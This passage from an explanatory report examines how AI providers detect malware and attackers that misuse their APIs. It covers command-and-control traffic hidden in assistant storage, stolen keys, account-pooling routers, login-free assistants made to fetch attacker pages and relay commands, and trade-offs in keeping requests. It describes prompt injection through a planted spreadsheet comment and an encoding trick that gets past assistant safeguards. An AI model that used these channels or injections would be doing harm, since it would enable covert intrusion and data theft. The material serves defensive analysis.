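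4. It encrypted the output, posted it as a new message and created an assistant marked "Result", which told the attackers to collect it.

The attackers used OpenAI's storage to pass messages and never ran a model, so a filter that checks prompts for harmful requests had nothing to check. OpenAI could see that an account kept creating and deleting assistants without running any, but the commands were encrypted.

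After Microsoft shared its findings, OpenAI disabled one key and the account it belonged to. The two companies confirmed that the account had made only limited calls and had not used any model. Microsoft doesn't say how long the attackers had used this channel. OpenAI had scheduled the Assistants interface for retirement in August 2026, but attackers have used email, Dropbox and other ordinary services in the same way for years.

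The discovery came from the victim's side because only the victim could see which program was connecting to OpenAI. Microsoft published a search for defenders that lists every program on a company's computers that connects to OpenAI's address, with the number of devices and days. A programming utility that has no AI features but contacts OpenAI every day is worth investigating.

### Where the provider loses sight of the attacker

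An attacker can hide from the provider, or do without one, in several ways.

| Method | What the model's provider receives | Account it can close |
|---|---|---|
| Stolen key | The whole request | The victim's |
| Pooled accounts behind a router | Requests from many people, mixed | One of many |
| Web assistant that needs no login | The request and the web address to open | None |
| Imitation of a model service | Nothing | None |
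| Open model on a private server | Nothing | None |

**Stolen keys.** A stolen key hides who sent a request but not what the request contains. Anthropic points out that the thief gets free computing and that the activity appears under the owner's name. The activist's software rotated through its stolen keys and mixed its requests with the owners' normal traffic.

Symantec recorded such requests with a decoy that posed as an unprotected AI service. The decoy received more than 127,000 requests from tens of thousands of addresses, according to Help Net Security's *Hackers hijack exposed AI models to launch cyberattacks at victims' expense*. Most were attempts to find models, use stolen keys or find exposed settings, so the total is not a count of hijackings. But one operator sent complete working instructions for an attacking agent. The instructions defined about 74 tools for scanning the internet,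 copying databases and controlling hijacked computers, and allowed up to 100,000 steps without human approval.

A provider that received those instructions would be unlikely to mistake them for ordinary work, even though one passage assured the model that reading password files was normal development. Closing the account would punish the victim, so it would be fairer to cancel only the key that was used and tell its owner. If the hijacked machine ran an open model locally, no provider would see the instructions. Zenity Labs' *Bring Your Own Agent* describes a similar intruder, who pointed what appears to have been OpenAI's Codex at Zenity's decoys and described it as a website auditor.

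A router can send many customers' requests through one account or spread one customer's requests over many accounts. Either way, no account shows what a single person is doing. Google's researchers saw a Chinese-linked group use two freely available programs, Claude-Relay-Service and CLI-Proxy-API, to pool accounts at Google, Anthropic and OpenAI. Another group tried a script that registers paid accounts, gets past the checks for automated sign-ups and cancels each subscription immediately, which gives the group replacements for accounts it loses.

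Google recommends that providers look for signs of such programs in their network data. This data can reveal a router, but not which of its users is the attacker. Closing the router's account would also cut off its other users, some of whom are developers with no other way to reach the model.

The attacker can also divide the work among providers. OpenAI's *Disrupting malicious uses of AI* (2026) reports that attackers may use different models at different stages. CLOSEDQUORUM was designed to send the same question to four providers, so each would see the question but not which action won the vote.

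**Assistants without a login.** In February 2026 Check Point Research's *AI in the Middle* (2026) demonstrated a method that needs neither a key nor an account. It uses the public web pages of two assistants, xAI's Grok and Microsoft's Copilot, which could open a web address on request:

1. The researchers built a website about Siamese cats, with a page that compared breeds.
2. Their test program collected some details of the computer it was on and added them, in encoded form, to the page's address.
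3. It opened Grok or Copilot in an invisible browser window and asked for a summary of that page.
4. The assistant fetched the page, which delivered the details to the researchers' server. The page listed each cat's "favourite Windows command", and the assistant included it in its summary.
5. The program picked the command out of the summary and ran it.

The company whose computer was infected would have seen only a connection to a well-known AI service. The assistants' safeguards sometimes blocked or cleaned up data that was obviously sensitive, but encoding the data was enough to get past them. Check Point reported the method to Microsoft and xAI, and didn't claim to have found anyone using it.

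The provider can see the address of the attacker's site and refuse to open it. It could also require a login before its assistant opens unfamiliar pages, which would let it close an attacker's account but would inconvenience honest visitors.

**Imitation.** Akamai found malware whose control server had an address ending in `/v1/chat/completions`, the ending that OpenAI introduced for requests to its models and many others have copied. The server was a small program in Tencent's cloud. The malware sent only a block of disguised text, with no access key, model name or conversation, and expected a disguised instruction back. Akamai thinks the attackers chose the address to look legitimate to network administrators, though it acknowledges that the server could in theory be passing requests to a model.

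No model provider can see this traffic. Tencent could shut the program down, and the victim could notice the odd format. Akamai examined 151 such addresses in its customers' traffic, and the conversations at all of them broadly followed OpenAI's format. But an attacker who reads OpenAI's documentation can add the missing fields in a few minutes.

**Private models.** When malware uses an open model on the attacker's own server, as PromptLock can, no AI provider can see or refuse its requests. LAMEHUG's model was also open, so its author could have run the model on a rented server after losing the access keys.

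Provider monitoring works best against attackers who want the strongest closed models or the least effort. Xanthorox and the group that attacked 30 AI companies suggest that there are many such attackers. The group said it wanted to reach an unreleased Claude model, but it never did. For a request like LAMEHUG's, which any decent programming model can answer, closing accounts mostly just makes the attacker switch to another model.

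### Warning an honest customer

Most of what a provider sees comes from customers who have done nothing wrong, and some of them receive harmful code. In the spreadsheet example, a supplier planted a comment telling the model to upload the file. The provider has the user's question about regional sales, the comment, and the Python containing the upload, which is enough to see that the code does more than the user asked. It also sees the model's original answer directly, not through a router.

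But the provider can't see what the application did with the code. It also may not know whether the customer wanted the upload, since a company might want a copy of every report on its own server. If the customer uses a router, the provider's warning goes to the router's operator, who has little reason to pass it on.

Some programming tools include checks of this kind. In 2023 GitHub added a filter to its Copilot assistant that checks suggestions before the programmer sees them and blocks those with common flaws, such as passwords written into the code or queries open to injection. It is unclear whether any provider routinely tells customers of its ordinary programming interface that an answer it has already delivered contained harmful code. Anthropic did inform victims of the intrusions it describes, but only after investigating an attacker.

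A warning service would be most useful for planted text that reaches many customers. Suppose a supplier sends 200 companies the same price list, which contains a hidden comment. Each company sees one strange file, if it notices at all. The provider could find the comment in one customer's request and then search other customers' requests for it, if it still has them.

### How long the provider keeps the text

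In 2025 OpenAI's standard terms for developers allowed it to keep requests and answers for up to 30 days to look for abuse. Customers with a good reason could apply to have none kept. Terms differ between providers and change often, so a developer has to read the current ones for the particular service and model.

Thirty days of storage would just have covered the activist's month on stolen keys if somebody had noticed on the last day, but it would cover little of an intrusion like the one Microsoft investigated. Longer storage might not have helped much there, since SesameOp's messages were encrypted. For malware that sends readable prompts, stored text is most useful after a tip from outside. If a security company finds a sample of the malware and shares its prompt, the provider can look up which other accounts sent that prompt and when they began. Without stored text, the provider can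 only watch for the prompt from then on.

Nearly all of the stored text belongs to honest people, though, which is the main privacy argument against storing it. The refund program's requests contain customers' names, orders and complaints, and the spreadsheet's sample rows may contain salaries or bank details. Thieves can steal stored text, employees can misuse it, and governments can ask for it. Anthropic publishes half-yearly reports on government requests. Courts can also override a provider's promise to delete text. In May 2025 a US court hearing The New York Times' copyright case ordered OpenAI to preserve answers that it would otherwise have deleted. The order lasted until September and exempted customers with a no-storage agreement.

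A provider that can search stored text for malware prompts can also search it for a lawyer's draft or a dissident's letter. A customer may trust the provider not to do that today and still not want it to keep the text.

The security case for storing requests rests on the HONESTCUE malware. If the provider deletes each request as soon as it has answered, its filter can check a harmless-looking prompt only once, and nobody can review the prompt after the malware is discovered. Attackers would choose a no-storage service if anyone could sign up for it, which is a good reason to make customers apply.

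A provider can look for abuse without keeping the text of every request. It can run its filter on each request while answering it, keep only the ones it flags, and delete the rest quickly. It can also store a hash of each request's standing instructions instead of the text. If a sample of malware with fixed instructions later appears, the provider can hash those instructions and look for matches. LAMEHUG would have been easy to find this way. But changing a single character of the instructions gives a new hash, and a malware author who knows about the method can do that for every victim.

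A customer can protect confidential data without waiting for the provider to settle this. The spreadsheet application can replace the sample rows with invented values of the same type, since the model needs only the column names and formats to write the code. The provider then stores nothing sensitive except the question. The refund program can remove names and addresses from a complaint before sending it to the provider.

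### When the provider is wrong

As with screening tool calls, most of a provider's alarms would be false even if its filter caught 90% of malicious requests and wrongly flagged only one honest request in 1,000, because malicious requests are presumably very rare.

Detection is much more accurate when the provider judges accounts instead of single requests. A developer who makes 500 calls a day would have about one request falsely flagged every two days, while an account used only by malware would have nine in ten of its requests flagged. A stolen key reduces this advantage because the thief's requests are mixed in with the owner's.

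A refusal does modest harm. The spreadsheet's user gets no answer to one question, perhaps because the table lists pesticides or the company tests security software. If the provider closes the developer's account, the question box stops working for every user, including those in the middle of a task, and the developer may need days to reach somebody who can reopen the account.

A fraudster could also deliberately get the shop's account closed by filling its complaint form with requests for malware, which the refund program would forward under that account. As a partial remedy, OpenAI lets developers send a scrambled identifier for each user, so that it can block one user without blocking the whole application. The shop could also limit how many complaints it accepts from one person, and use a separate account for the refund program so that closing it wouldn't take down everything else.

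The refund program's fallback, described in an earlier section, handles a refusal badly. It treats any reply other than "approve" or "refer" as a failure and tries the backup model. If the main model refused because the complaint contained an attack, the program would send the same attack to a model that may be easier to fool. Some providers mark a refusal separately from an error, and the program should use that mark where it exists:

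```
if was_refused(answer):
    return "refer"
```

The two lines go before the check for a valid label. A staff member then reads the complaint, which adds one case when the refusal was a false alarm.
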